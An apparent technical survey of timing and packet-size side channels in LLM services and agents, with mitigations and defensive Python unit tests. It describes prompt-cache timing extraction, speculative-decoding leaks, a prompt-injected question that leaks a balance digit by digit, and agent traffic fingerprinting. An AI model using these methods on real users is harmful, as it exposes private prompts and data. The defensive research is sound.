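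On their own server, Song and colleagues flooded the cache with unrelated requests until it dropped the old entries. They could then recover another user's instructions one token at a time. A model trained on similar prompts proposed the next token, and the response time indicated whether the proposal was right. A single timing detected 88% of cache hits, with false alarms on 10% of misses. With a majority vote over ten timings, these figures became 99% and 0.3%. If the errors had been independent, the false-alarm rate would have fallen to about 0.015%, so some of the noise probably persisted from one timing to the next.

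The attack needed about 111 queries for each recovered token. At best it recovered 81 tokens of one prompt, but it averaged only about 12 tokens even on the half of the 200 targets where it was more successful. Gu and colleagues doubt that the attack is a practical threat yet. They could not extract prompts from real services, and the attack ran without internet delays and relied on clearing the cache. However, they expect known templates with blanks for personal details to be easier targets.

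How much a bank assistant's response times reveal depends heavily on where the balance sits in the template. If it follows 5,000 tokens of fixed instructions, a correct guess lengthens the match by only a few tokens, and the time difference is tiny. If it comes before the instructions, a correct guess matches all 5,000 tokens and a wrong one matches almost none, so it is safer for developers to put the secret last. The attacker would still have to guess the exact balance before the cache entry expires, which at OpenAI and Anthropic took about five minutes without use. But if the template says only "balance: low" or "balance: healthy", two guesses are enough.

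### Speculative decoding

A large model needs about as much time to check several proposed tokens as to generate one, because it can check them all at once. Speculative decoding takes advantage of this by having a small, fast model propose, for example, the next five tokens. The large model keeps the tokens before the first one it rejects and replaces that one with its own. The process then repeats. Each step therefore produces more tokens when the text is predictable.

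Carlini and Nasr (2024) showed in *Remote Timing Attacks on Efficient Language Model Inference* that an eavesdropper can exploit this difference in pace. They could not see which techniques OpenAI used, but they found that the June 2023 version of GPT-4 answered easy and hard questions at the same speed, while the April 2024 version was twice as fast on easy ones. From packet times alone, they could tell with 94.7% accuracy whether a user had asked GPT-3.5 for the first 50 numbers or for 50 random ones.

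Telling two known requests apart is an easy case. On the ChatGPT website, using packet sizes as well as response times, the researchers could distinguish medical from programming questions about 80% of the time and identify a story's language from ten options about 49% of the time. When they trained an attack on GPT-3.5 and kept testing it, its accuracy stayed high for about a month and then dropped to chance, probably because OpenAI had changed something, so an eavesdropper would have to keep retraining the attack.

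Carlini and Nasr's experiment with Claude 3 Opus shows why treating time and length as separate problems can be a mistake. The server sometimes put several tokens in one packet, which disrupted the timing pattern and limited accuracy to 60%. When they used packet sizes to work out how many tokens each packet held, accuracy rose to 100%.

An attacker who can also add text to the prompt can ask about the secret directly. The researchers hid a number from 1 to 1,000 in a prompt and looked for a question that the large model could answer and the small one could not. They settled on "When looking at that number, is X the initial digit? Yes or no?" The small model always answered no. If X was the right digit, the large model usually disagreed, which delayed the second token of the reply. In 97.2% of cases, this revealed whether the guess was right, compared with 56.2% for a plainer wording. The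 rate seems to come from comparing the two models' answers on one machine, so network noise would lower it.

Prompt injection could give an attacker the same opportunity against the bank assistant. A web page could contain the question, and an accomplice on the network could time the reply without reading it. Finding one digit takes at most nine questions, so finding a six-digit balance takes at most 54.

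Later work suggests that sizes reveal speculation more reliably than times do. In *When Speculation Spills Secrets*, Wei, Abdulrazzag and colleagues (2024) ran a model on a server more than 1,500 miles from the user and tried to identify which of 50 medical questions the user had asked, a task where random guessing would succeed 2% of the time.

| Randomness setting of the model | Packet sizes | Packet times | Packet times, busy server (simulated) |
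|---|---|---|---|
| 0.3 (low) | 77.6% | 14.4% | 6.4% |
| 0.6 | 65.6% | 6.0% | 4.0% |
| 0.8 | 44.8% | 5.2% | 2.4% |
| 1.0 (high) | 24.0% | 4.8% | 2.8% |

The size attack also used timing, so it is not entirely separate from the timing attack. It combined packets that arrived within 55 milliseconds of each other to work out which tokens had come from the same step. A defence that spaced tokens evenly in time might therefore weaken both attacks.

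Some versions of speculative decoding take their proposed tokens from a store of earlier text. A user who sees several tokens arrive together can infer that the sequence is in the store. Wei and colleagues extracted about 200,000 distinct sequences in three hours from a store of 120,000 conversations by repeatedly asking for text that continued what had already leaked. They recommend filling such stores only with public or anonymized text.

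### Separate caches

Giving each user a separate cache stops one user from detecting another's prompts. Gu and colleagues expect this to keep most of the savings from caching, because different users rarely send prompts with long identical beginnings.

That holds for a provider's direct customers but not always for an agent. Thousands of people may use one bank assistant, and the model provider may see them all as a single customer because the developer sends every request under one account. Song and colleagues built a document summarizer that worked this way on DeepSeek's service. By timing its replies, one user could tell whether another had uploaded a particular document, with an average accuracy of 89% and a false-alarm rate of 5%.

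A developer can separate users by starting each one's prompt with a different secret random string, since the cache matches prompts only from the beginning. But then users can't share the stored work for the assistant's long instructions, which are the same for everyone. Song and colleagues tried a compromise in which prompts share stored work only in blocks of several tokens, so an attacker has to guess a whole block at once. Blocks of four slowed their attack but didn't stop it, reducing its recovery rate from 91.5% to 49.0% and raising the queries needed per token from 215 to 471.

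The provider can also delay fast replies to match slow ones. Users lose the speed, but the provider still saves the computation. Unlike separate caches, this delay stops an eavesdropper from using an unusually fast first token to infer that the user has sent similar text before.

### Holding replies back

The same reasoning applies to any source of delay. Suppose the assistant takes exactly three seconds when the balance is healthy and eleven when it is low, and the two cases are equally common. An eavesdropper sees only the time at which the complete reply arrives.

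| Rule for sending the reply | How often the eavesdropper learns whether the balance is low | Average added delay |
|---|---|---|
| Send at once | Always | None |
| Add a random delay of 0 to 10 seconds | 80% of runs | 5 seconds |
| Send at the next multiple of 5 seconds | Always (5 seconds or 15) | 3 seconds |
| Hold until 11 seconds | Never | 4 seconds |
| Hold until 15 seconds | Never | 8 seconds |

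Random delay adds more waiting time here than holding every reply until eleven seconds, and it still leaks information about the balance. Total response times under eleven seconds occur only when the balance is healthy, and those over thirteen seconds only when it is low. After two runs, the eavesdropper has a 96% probability of knowing whether the balance is healthy or low.

A wider range of delays would only force the eavesdropper to observe more runs, as with random padding. The added delay has the same average whatever the balance is, so the two average response times would still differ by eight seconds. *Deterministically Deterring Timing Attacks in Deterland* (2015) notes that added noise controls timing channels only for particular workloads, and that other researchers have built covert channels that work despite the noise.

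Holding replies until a worst-case time works only if no run takes longer than that. This is hard to guarantee with agents, because a model can write more than usual and a website can hang. Suppose replies are held for 15 seconds, and 2% of runs take longer when the balance is low, compared with 0.1% when it is healthy. A single late reply then raises the probability of a low balance from 50% to 95%. If the assistant runs once a day and the balance stays low for a month, there is a 45% chance of at least one late reply.

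The assistant could instead stop at 15 seconds and send an error message of the usual size. That reply would look normal to an eavesdropper, but the user would probably ask again, and the extra request is visible. Raising the limit to 60 seconds would make late runs rarer, but every user would wait a minute, even for an answer that was ready in three seconds.

Sending at fixed intervals adds less delay, but the interval has to be long enough to cover the difference it is meant to hide. In the example, sending only at multiples of 15 seconds would hide the difference, but multiples of five would not. Choosing the release times individually can reduce the leak with less delay. Suppose an assistant has four equally common response times of 3, 4, 10 and 11 seconds, which reveal two bits. Delaying the 3-second replies to 4 seconds and the 10-second ones to 11 adds half a second on average and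 leaves one bit. Delaying everything to 11 seconds removes that bit but adds four seconds on average. *Quantitative Mitigation of Timing Side Channels* (2019) treats this as an optimization problem, where a developer limits the overhead and merges groups of response times to leak as little as possible. When every merge has to be all or nothing, the problem is NP-hard, meaning that no known method solves every large case quickly.

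For streamed replies, Carlini and Nasr proposed sending one token at a fixed interval, with an empty message whenever no token is ready. Sending a message every 10 milliseconds would cause almost no noticeable delay for users but increase traffic by 50% to 300%. Sending one every 80 milliseconds would increase traffic by less than 10% and delay each token by 4 to 13 milliseconds.

This hides the pace of the text, which their attacks used, but not when the text ends. At 80 milliseconds a token, a 50-token reply lasts four seconds and a 400-token reply lasts 32. To hide the length, the server has to keep sending empty messages, the same size as the real ones, until a fixed end time.

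If the assistant delays only the final reply, a tool server can still time the gaps between the calls it receives. The program around the model could hold every tool result for a fixed time before passing it on. An eavesdropper next to the tool would still see how fast the tool answered, and only the tool's operator can change that.

### Predictive mitigation

A fixed limit has to be set high from the start, because nobody knows in advance how long the slowest run will take. In *Predictive black-box mitigation of timing channels*, Askarov, Zhang and Myers (2010) proposed raising the limit only when an output misses it. Their mitigator releases outputs on a predicted schedule and holds any that are ready early until their slot. If an output isn't ready in time, the prediction has failed, and the mitigator switches to a slower schedule. The schedule contains no secrets, so information leaks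 only when a prediction fails.

For the assistant, the rule could start with a four-second limit and double it after each miss. While the balance is healthy, every reply arrives after exactly four seconds. The first low-balance reply takes eleven seconds to produce, so it misses the limits of four and eight seconds and goes out at sixteen. From then on, every reply arrives after sixteen seconds. The eavesdropper learns when the balance first became low but cannot tell whether it later recovered.

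Counting the possible timings gives a bound on the total leak under the mitigator. Suppose no reply takes more than sixteen seconds, so the limit is always 4, 8 or 16 seconds and never shrinks. The timing of 1,000 replies then depends only on at which replies the limit grew. There are 1,002 × 1,001 / 2 = 501,501 possibilities, which carry at most 18.9 bits, and another 1,000 replies would raise this maximum by only two bits. If each reply could freely take any of three times, the maximum for 1,000 replies would be 1,585 bits.

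A balance with a million possible values contains only 19.9 bits, so the bound by itself guarantees little protection for the bank assistant. The actual leak is probably much smaller, because response times tend to depend on whether the balance is low rather than on its exact value.

A bound on total leakage also does not measure how evenly the risk is spread. Wei, Harris and colleagues argue that predictive mitigation can leave certain secrets, which they call "tail victims", far more exposed than the rest. In the example, a customer who runs low once in three years reveals the exact day this happens.

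When a response misses the time limit, everyone who uses the assistant afterward waits longer. One hung website can lengthen the limit permanently, even if the delay had nothing to do with the balance. *Deterministically Deterring Timing Attacks in Deterland* describes the same problem in virtual machines, whose workloads are hard to predict and whose timing varies mostly for harmless reasons. A developer could lower the limit every night, but then the assistant could leak again every day.

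Better predictions reduce the number of misses. *Predictive mitigation of timing channels in interactive systems* (Zhang, Askarov and Myers, 2011) extended the method to services that answer requests from many clients, and let the prediction depend on any public information. The assistant could then have one limit for questions about the weather and a longer one for questions about holidays. This is safe only if the type of question is public, because otherwise an eavesdropper could infer it from the delay.

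## What can an eavesdropper infer from a whole agent session?

An agent session alternates between model calls and tool calls, with waits in between, and may include retries and file downloads, whereas a chat reply is one stream of text. An eavesdropper sees bursts of traffic and pauses in a pattern that depends on what the agent is doing.

Zhang, Deng and colleagues (2025), in *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis*, recorded such patterns between users and agents on ChatGPT's website. A literature search produced a quick call followed by a long stretch of text. A diagram-drawing agent sent a description, made one call containing the whole layout, and then paused while an outside service drew the diagram. Plain conversation produced a fairly even flow of traffic.

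An eavesdropper sees more when the agent runs on the user's own computer, because its tool calls also cross the network being watched. Li, Gao and colleagues (2026) give an example in *ANT* from Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. When Claude Code searches the web, nearly all the traffic goes to the model's server, which carries out the search. When it fetches a page, the eavesdropper also sees a domain-name lookup and a download from another server.

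### Recognising an agent

AgentPrint, an attack by Zhang and colleagues, divides each recording into 1,800 equal time slices. For each slice, it counts the packets and adds up the bytes in each direction. Every session therefore becomes a grid of 4 × 1,800 = 7,200 numbers, however many packets it contained. The packet counts mainly capture the rhythm of the work, and the byte totals help distinguish text from images and files. A neural network then learns which grids belong to which agent.

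The researchers tested 50 popular "GPTs", customised versions of ChatGPT that users build and share. They wrote 150 prompts for each, designed to make it use its special functions, and discarded text-only replies under 500 characters. These choices made the agents easier to recognise, but giving identical prompts to similar agents made the test harder.

AgentPrint distinguished five behaviours with 94.1% accuracy: calling an outside service, analysing documents or data, generating an image, sending the user to a link, and replying in plain text. It identified the agent with an average F1 score of 0.866 in a closed-world test, where the user is known to be using one of 50 agents. In an open-world test, the user may be using some other agent, so the attacker must first decide whether the agent is one of the 50.

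| Traffic the eavesdropper sees | F1, closed world | F1, open world |
|---|---|---|
| Only the connection to ChatGPT | 0.824 | 0.812 |
| Everything the browser sends and receives | 0.866 | 0.848 |

The small drop in the open-world test is weak evidence that the attack would work in practice. The test added only 428 sessions with unlisted agents to 7,311 with listed ones, so about 94% of sessions involved a listed agent. Users had created more than 755,000 GPTs by October 2024. Even if none of the 428 sessions had caused a false alarm, the true false-alarm rate could be as high as 0.7%. If an attacker were looking for a medical agent that accounts for one session in 1,000, with a false-alarm rate of 0.7% and a detection rate of 85%, only about 11% of the alarms would be correct.

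### From agents to occupations

Zhang and colleagues also tried to infer a user's occupation group from the agents they use. For the simulated users, one language model described a working day in a given occupation, and another chose five suitable agents. The real users were 49 people who said which of 55 agents they would probably use at work. The researchers captured no traffic from these people and instead added random errors to their answers to imitate AgentPrint's mistakes.

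The attack named the right group among its top three guesses for 73.9% of simulated users and 69.1% of real ones. Someone who always named the commonest groups in each sample would have done nearly as well on the real users:

| Users | First guess right | Always naming the commonest group | Right group in top three | Always naming the three commonest |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Simulated | 41.2% | 21.2% | 73.9% | 51.7% |
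| Real | 46.3% | 26.5% | 69.1% | 67.3% |

The first guesses suggest that an eavesdropper can learn something about a person's work from their choice of agents. But the simulated sample included only occupations in which language models can help with many tasks. When the researchers included all 923 occupations in their database, the top-three figure fell to 58.9%.

### Recognising a team's task

Pouryousef and colleagues studied teams of two to five agents working on tasks in ten categories, such as bargaining, bug fixing and contract analysis. In "graph" teams, every agent could write to every other, while in "star" teams a central planner handled all communication. The eavesdropper saw the encrypted traffic between the agents and their model, but not the messages between agents. The eavesdropper's classifier had to identify the category of each task without having seen that task in training.

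| What the classifier received | Graph teams | Star teams |
|---|---|---|
| All features of the whole team's traffic | 85.3% | 86.0% |
| Traffic of up to four agents | 84.3% | 85.9% |
| Traffic of one agent | 66.5% | 78.0% |
| Whole team, without any size features | 54.0% | 58.7% |
| Nothing (random guessing) | 10% | 10% |

The abstract reports accuracy of up to 90.7%, but the highest figure in the detailed results is 86.0%, and accuracy is much lower for a single agent's traffic. The abstract lists 2,838 team runs, but the methods section reports that 3,970 were kept, so it is unclear how many the results are based on.

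All the agents used the same small model, Llama 3.2 with 3 billion parameters, on the researchers' own server. The recordings came from a connection inside that machine, so they contain no internet delays. The most useful features described the size of the agents' requests to the model. Since most categories came from different benchmarks, the classifier may partly have recognised the typical length of a contract or bug report. Its accuracy also depended on how the team of agents was organised, falling from 83% to 52% when it was trained on one kind of team and tested on the other.

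### Spotting malicious work

In ANT, the observer is a company that wants to check what agents on its network are doing without reading their messages. Li and colleagues recorded 3,114 runs of agents on 20 tasks, three of which involved cyberattacks. They then tested 13 existing traffic analysis methods, none of which was designed for agents.

The test set had 189 harmless runs and 20 malicious ones, so labeling every run harmless would be 90.4% accurate. All 13 methods for detecting malicious runs were more than 90% accurate, but seven of them caught fewer than half of the malicious runs.

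Detection depended heavily on the type of attack. Four methods caught nearly all the attacks on a website, where the agent scans for weaknesses and sends unusual requests, but none of the runs in which an agent wrote malicious code or tried to escape a restricted environment. An agent writing malicious code makes much the same calls as one writing ordinary code, and encryption hides the difference. Some of the other methods did fairly well on all three attack tasks, so the traffic contains clues, but 20 runs are too few to measure these methods' success precisely.

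The methods also had trouble with finer distinctions. In 72.7% of runs, the best one correctly identified which of five broad kinds of work the agent was doing. Across all the methods, 35.1% of runs in which the agent assessed scientific evidence were misclassified as general question answering, since both consist mostly of searching, reading and writing. When the methods had to place single steps into 47 groups, their accuracy was between 35.5% and 46.2%, compared with 25% for always guessing "search".

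An eavesdropper may not need the whole session to recognise what kind of work an agent is doing. When Li and colleagues retrained eight recognition methods on only the traffic to and from the model, average accuracy rose by 5.6 percentage points. When they used only the remaining traffic, it fell by 4.3 points. Encrypting or rerouting one part of the traffic would therefore leave useful evidence in the other.

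### Following a research agent across the web

*Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents* (Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues, 2025) studies agents that run on the user's computer and gather information from many websites. Such an agent typically visits 70 to 140 domains for one request. Even when the pages are encrypted, an internet provider can often see the domain names, because the computer sends them unencrypted when it looks them up or opens a connection. Visits to a bank, a debt charity and two lenders within a minute would suggest that the user has money problems.

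The attacker runs the same kind of agent on other prompts and records the domains it visits. The attacker then gives a language model five of these prompts, each with its domains, and the victim's list of domains, and asks for the victim's prompt. GPT-4 scored each guess against the original prompt on scales from 0 to 1. In the best-known result, the guesses averaged 0.77 for having the same purpose and 0.735 for needing the same kind of source.

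The abstract describes this as recovering more than 73% of the "functional and domain knowledge" in the prompts, which is not the same as recovering 73% of the prompts. A guess about work visas in southern Europe counts as a success if the user asked about digital nomad visas in Italy and Spain. The average score for matching the actual subject was only 0.52. The test had 20 prompts. Two other agents leaked less, with scores of 0.54 to 0.63 for purpose and kind of source.

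Jeong and colleagues also linked seven sessions from each invented user and recovered up to 19 of 32 personal traits. They had written some of these traits into the users' prompts, openly or by implication, so real users might reveal less. The attack also assumes that the domain names are visible. Encrypting lookups and connection names, or using a virtual private network (VPN), would hide many of them from the internet provider, but the VPN's operator could still see them.

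### How far do the results carry over?

Except in AgentPrint's small open-world test, the classifiers chose from a list of categories fixed in advance, so an agent doing something else would still get one of the listed labels. ANT may also make recognition too easy, because it splits runs at random within each task and its 3,114 runs cover only 659 distinct problems. The same problem can therefore appear in both training and testing.

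Clean recordings also help the attacker. Pouryousef and colleagues used the agents' own logs to cut the traffic into separate runs, and Li and colleagues gave each run its own isolated network. AgentPrint assumes that the user talks to one agent at a time and does nothing else online. In a real household, an eavesdropper has to find the session among video calls and software updates, and two agents may be working at once. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026) adds that traffic analysis needs separate training for each agent and provider and does not identify the user or program responsible.

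An attacker who can influence the agent may avoid some of these difficulties. *SkillWatermark* (2026) describes prompts that turn the side channel into a covert channel by making an agent produce recognisable traffic patterns. The attacker then doesn't need to train a classifier on a fixed list of prompts.

An eavesdropper can also combine weak evidence from many sessions. If guesses about whether the balance is low are right 60% of the time from one session, a majority vote over 31 sessions is right about 87% of the time. This assumes that the true answer is the same in every session and that the errors are independent. An internet provider can easily link the sessions because it knows which customer they belong to.

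### What padding leaves visible

Suppose the bank assistant runs on the user's computer and pads every message to 8,000 bytes. When the balance is healthy, the assistant asks the model for a plan, asks the bank for the balance, and asks the model for an answer. When the balance is low, it also fetches the overdraft terms and then asks the model again. The eavesdropper counts three exchanges when the balance is healthy and five when it is low. Padding hides the size of each message but doesn't change the number of exchanges, their order or the pauses between them.

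When Pouryousef and colleagues removed all the size features, which roughly imitates perfect padding, their classifier still recognised the task more than five times as often as chance. AgentPrint's threat model assumes a service that already pads its messages and sends several tokens together.

Session-level traffic shaping is meant to make every session look the same to an eavesdropper. In its strictest form, the agent's computer sends and receives packets of one size at fixed intervals, between fixed start and end times, with dummy packets when there is no real data to send. Every request and result waits for the next scheduled packet. A retry or an extra tool call replaces dummy packets, so it doesn't change the pattern.

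Sending packets at a constant rate can waste bandwidth and slow large transfers. With one 1,250-byte packet in each direction every 50 milliseconds, a 60-second session carries 1.5 megabytes each way, even if the agent needs only 100 kilobytes. If the agent downloads a 5-megabyte file, the transfer takes 200 seconds at that rate. The developer must use at least 3.3 times the bandwidth in every session to keep sessions at 60 seconds, make every session last at least 200 seconds, or let the eavesdropper see that some sessions run longer.

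The shaping also has to hide where the traffic goes. Even if each connection carries a steady flow, a new connection to the bank's website still reveals the overdraft lookup. The agent could send everything through one encrypted tunnel to a relay, which contacts the websites. But the relay can see the destinations, and so can an eavesdropper between the relay and the websites unless the relay mixes many users' traffic.

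Jeong and colleagues tested lower-overhead defences that change what the agent does. Some added decoy prompts or imitated other users, while others sent the agent to general-purpose websites or had the model answer from its own knowledge. These defences reduced the attack's success by an average of 29% with little effect on the quality of the results. Zhang and colleagues suggest dummy packets, batching and shaping but publish no measurements of them, and Pouryousef and colleagues leave shaping to future work.

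A developer could also use a few standard session patterns, such as a short one and a long one. With two patterns, the choice of pattern reveals at most one bit per session, though the leakage adds up over many sessions. Even a single pattern doesn't hide when sessions take place. If the assistant starts a session automatically whenever the balance runs low, an eavesdropper who sees one start can infer that the balance is low. To prevent this, the assistant would have to run on a fixed schedule.

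## How can unit tests check control-flow and length mitigations?

An ordinary unit test checks one run at a time. A test of the assistant might set the balance to 900, ask whether the user can afford a holiday, and check that no outgoing message contains "900". That test passes even if the assistant fetches the bank's overdraft terms. The fetch reveals information about the balance only because the assistant would not have made it with a balance of 1,100, and a test run only with 900 cannot detect that difference.

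*Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) distinguishes trace properties, which each run obeys or breaks on its own, from hyperproperties, which are rules about a whole set of runs. A ban on writing to the network after reading a file is a trace property. Noninterference is a hyperproperty and not a trace property, because whether one run is acceptable depends on what the system does in other runs.

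If a deterministic system violates noninterference, two runs with different secrets are enough to show it. In *Secure Information Flow by Self-Composition*, Barthe, D'Argenio and Rezk (2004) turned this into a way to prove programs secure. They join a program to a copy of itself in which every variable is renamed, so the two halves cannot affect each other. Comparing two runs of the original program then becomes checking that, in a single run of the combined program, public variables that match at the start still match at the end.

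A proof of this kind covers every possible secret. A paired-run test applies the same idea to only two chosen secrets, so it is much easier to write.

### A scripted model and recording tools

The comparison only makes sense if the runs differ in nothing but the secret. A live model breaks this condition because it samples its responses. *Software Verification of Hyperproperties Beyond k-Safety* (2022) points out that random choices alone can make a program fail the simple two-run check. Tests with a live model therefore need to compare distributions statistically, and *PACE* (2026) notes that a finite sample cannot conclusively show that two distributions differ. A unit test can avoid this problem by replacing the model with a script that always gives the same response to the same history.

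The tools need replacing too, since a test should not email a real adviser. These fake tools record each call's name, arguments, size in bytes and any error, in the order in which the calls arrive:

```
import json

class FakeTools:
    def __init__(self, balance):
        self.balance = balance
        self.log = []

    def call(self, name, **args):
        body = json.dumps({"tool": name, "args": args}).encode("utf-8")
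        short = name == "transfer" and args["amount"] > self.balance
        error = "insufficient funds" if short else None
        self.log.append((name, args, len(body), error))
        if error:
            raise RuntimeError(error)
        return self.balance if name == "get_balance" else "ok"

def outsider(log):
    bank_calls = ("get_balance", "transfer")
    return [entry for entry in log if entry[0] not in bank_calls]
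```

The log contains everything, including calls to the bank. The function `outsider` keeps only what a particular observer can see, which here is email and web requests but not bank calls. This function is the O in the definition of noninterference. To test against a different observer, the developer changes this function and leaves the fake tools alone.

Next come the scripted model and the agent:

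```
def scripted_model(results):
    if not results:
        return "get_balance", {}
    low = results[0] < 1000
    if low and len(results) == 1:
        return "fetch", {"page": "overdraft terms"}
    return "reply", {"text": "Only on overdraft." if low else "Yes."}

def run_agent(model, tools, prefetch=True):
    stored, results = {}, []
    if prefetch:
        page = "overdraft terms"
        stored[page] = tools.call("fetch", page=page)
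    while True:
        name, args = model(results)
        if name == "reply":
            return args["text"]
        if name == "fetch" and args["page"] in stored:
            results.append(stored[args["page"]])
        else:
            results.append(tools.call(name, **args))
```

The script requests the balance, then requests the overdraft terms if the balance is below 1,000, and then replies. The agent implements the mitigation by fetching the terms at the start of every run. If the model calls for them later, the agent uses the stored copy and sends no request.

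The script has to behave like a model that would leak, because if it ignored the balance, even an agent with no mitigation would pass. Garby and colleagues' LLMbda interpreter suits this kind of test because it is deterministic and takes the model's responses from a separate part, called an oracle, which a developer could replace with a script.

### Failing, passing and failing again

The test runs the agent with balances of 900 and 1,100, on either side of the threshold:

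```
def observe(balance, **options):
    tools = FakeTools(balance)
    reply = run_agent(scripted_model, tools, **options)
    return outsider(tools.log), reply

def test_requests_do_not_depend_on_balance():
    low_trace, low_reply = observe(900)
    high_trace, high_reply = observe(1100)
    assert low_reply == "Only on overdraft."
    assert high_reply == "Yes."
    assert low_trace == high_trace
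```

A developer should first run this test on the leaking program, with `prefetch` off, and check that it fails. The developer should then turn the mitigation on and check that the test passes, then turn it off again and check that the failure returns.

| `prefetch` | Trace at 900 | Trace at 1,100 | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Off | One fetch of 54 bytes | Empty | Fails |
| On | One fetch of 54 bytes | One fetch of 54 bytes | Passes |
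| Off again | One fetch of 54 bytes | Empty | Fails |

The last row matters because a test can pass even if the mitigation doesn't work. The developer may have changed the test while writing the fix, or `outsider` may filter out the request that leaks. If the test still passes without the mitigation, its earlier pass was not evidence that the mitigation worked.

The developer can make this check permanent by adding a second test:

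```
def test_leak_returns_without_prefetch():
    low_trace, _ = observe(900, prefetch=False)
    high_trace, _ = observe(1100, prefetch=False)
    assert low_trace != high_trace
```

The drawback is that the agent now has a switch that disables its protection, so the developer has to make sure nobody can use it in the live service.

The two assertions about the replies catch an agent that does nothing, which would pass any test that only compares traces because its traces are identical and empty. They confirm that the agent finished its task and that the balance reached the model.

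Running the same balance twice is also useful. If those traces differ, something other than the secret is changing, such as a timestamp, a random request number or a cache that the first run filled. *Attributing Security Outcomes in LLM-Agent Evaluations* (2026) illustrates this problem in security benchmarks with a hypothetical test case, run twice with only the hash seed changed. The hash seed is a number that can affect details such as the order in which Python iterates over a set. If the verdict changes, nobody can attribute the change to the agent, the attack or the defence. A paired-run test should therefore fix the seed and the clock, and start both runs with empty caches.

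Fixing the seed makes the test stricter than the definition for random systems. If an agent adds random padding to its messages, using the same seed gives both runs the same padding, so any difference in length remains and the test fails. The failure doesn't show how much the padding helps, which again has to be measured statistically.

### Pairs that straddle a boundary

A paired-run test can only detect a leak that separates its two secrets. Suppose a developer caps a loop with a secret bound at five requests:

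```
def ping(tools):
    for _ in range(min(tools.call("get_balance"), 5)):
        tools.call("fetch", page="ping")
```

With balances of 3 and 7, the server receives three requests in the first run and five in the second, so the test fails and exposes the remaining leak. With balances of 7 and 9, it receives five requests in both runs and the test passes.

The test with balances of 7 and 9 fails without the cap, as it should, because the server receives seven requests for one and nine for the other, and it passes once the cap is in place. Removing the fix therefore does not reveal that 7 and 9 are a bad choice. They show that the cap works for large balances, but every balance below five still produces its own number of requests.

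If the agent instead makes exactly five requests every time, the test also passes with 3 and 7. To check this, the developer should try balances just below, at and above the cap, along with zero and a very large number.

A test can check every pair of traces without a separate run for each pair. If each of eight traces equals the first, they all equal one another, so eight runs cover all 28 pairs.

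One of Tallam and Miller's suggestions for loops is to combine requests. If the agent sends all its pings as a single list, it always makes one call, but the call's size still varies with the number of pings. With the format above, a list of three takes 62 bytes and a list of seven takes 94. A test that compares only the names of the calls would miss this difference, which is why the log includes sizes.

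A test can detect a branch only if its two balances are on opposite sides of the threshold. Balances of 900 and 1,100 reveal a branch at 1,000 but miss one at 5,000. They also miss a condition such as `950 < balance < 1050`, because both are outside the range. Developers who can read the code should take the constants from it and test values around each one. Thresholds that a live model uses in its judgement are harder to find because they aren't written down.

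Sometimes the user wants the branch to reveal something, as with the rule to email the adviser if the balance exceeds 10,000. A test that compares 9,000 with 11,000 would fail even if the assistant did what the user asked. Barthe and colleagues handle a similar case, a program that checks a PIN and has to reveal whether the user's guess was right. They require matching results only for secrets that give the same answer to that guess.

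For the adviser, this means comparing balances on the same side of the threshold. The traces for 0 and 10,000 should match, and so should those for 10,001 and 900,000. If the assistant adds "you have plenty to invest" to the email when the balance is above 500,000, the second pair of traces will differ.

### Errors, skipped branches and retries

To test the error channel, the developer can reuse the earlier program that transfers 5,000 and then emails the adviser. The fake `transfer` tool raises an exception if the balance is too low, so the test should compare balances of 4,999 and 5,000. Balances of 900 and 1,100 would miss the leak because the transfer fails for both. The test has to catch the exception so that it can compare the traces, one of which is empty.

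The test passes if the program catches the exception and always emails "I have dealt with the transfer request". It still fails if the program catches the exception but emails the adviser only after a successful transfer, so it distinguishes a complete fix from a partial one. The test should also check that the trace contains an email, in case both runs stop early for an unrelated reason.

A unit test for the untaken-branch leak has to test the interpreter rather than a single agent program. The developer runs the five-line program that Garby and colleagues used against CaMeL, sets its threshold to 1,000, and compares the emails for values of 900 and 1,100. A simpler program that sends an email directly inside the branch wouldn't reveal this leak, because CaMeL's interpreter already blocks that program.

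A test's result can depend on whether the trace records how the run ended. Under the no-high-upgrade rule, a test that compares only emails passes, but one that also compares how the runs ended fails because the program stops early at 1,100. Two separate tests are best, because only some observers can tell whether a run finished. An interpreter passes both if it analyses the whole program and rejects it before running it.

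Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge that their multi-agent version of CaMeL has the same leak because it extends the same interpreter. A test written for one system is therefore useful for others built on it, and for later versions of the interpreter that might reintroduce the leak.

Retries need a test that includes the loop around the interpreter. A test that makes only one attempt can show at most one bit of leakage, which a developer might accept. Clarkson and Schneider give an example of a rule that no pair of runs can test. Suppose a system splits a secret into k parts, all needed to recover it, and outputs one part per run. Showing that the system has leaked the whole secret can take k runs.

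For CaMeL's retry loop, the test can play the attacker and carry out the binary search:

```
def search(was_blocked):
    low, high = 0, 1023
    while low < high:
        middle = (low + high) // 2
        if was_blocked(middle):
            low = middle + 1
        else:
            high = middle
    return low

def test_retries_do_not_reveal_balance():
    guesses = set()
    for balance in (3, 900, 1000):
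        guesses.add(search(lambda t: attempt(balance, t)))
    assert len(guesses) == 1
```

The developer supplies a function, `attempt`, which gives the agent a program that sends an email if the balance exceeds t. The function returns whether the retry loop registered a failure. If the interpreter blocks the email only when the program tries to send it, the search finds all three balances in ten attempts each, and the test fails. If the interpreter rejects the program whatever the balance is, all three searches end at 1,023 and the test passes.

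The choice of balances matters here too. Suppose the developer stops the agent's search after three attempts. The balances 900 and 1,000 are both above the first three thresholds (511, 767 and 895), so a test with only those two would pass. A test that also includes a balance of 3 would fail, because the agent still leaks.

### Measuring length

A test for the length channel should count bytes in the form in which the agent sends them. This function pads each message to a multiple of 256 bytes by adding spaces, which JSON, the data format, allows at the end:

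```
def frame(text, bucket=256):
    data = json.dumps({"text": text}).encode("utf-8")
    return data + b" " * (-len(data) % bucket)

def test_bucket_edges():
    sizes = [len(frame("x" * n)) for n in (243, 244, 245)]
    assert sizes == [256, 256, 512]
```

The JSON wrapper takes 12 bytes, so texts of 243, 244 and 245 characters produce messages just below, at and just above the edge of the first bucket. Testing 244 characters catches the common mistake of adding `bucket - len(data) % bucket` spaces. This works for nearly every length, but it adds a whole extra bucket when the message already fits exactly.

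This test confirms only that the padding function works as intended. Checking whether the padding hides the balance requires a paired run with the assistant's real replies. With the earlier replies of 120 and 1,800 bytes, the paired-run test fails even though `test_bucket_edges` passes. The paired-run test passes with 2,048-byte buckets, but only because both replies fit in one bucket. The developer should also test the longest reply the assistant can send, which fits in one 2,048-byte bucket only if it has at most 2,036 plain characters.

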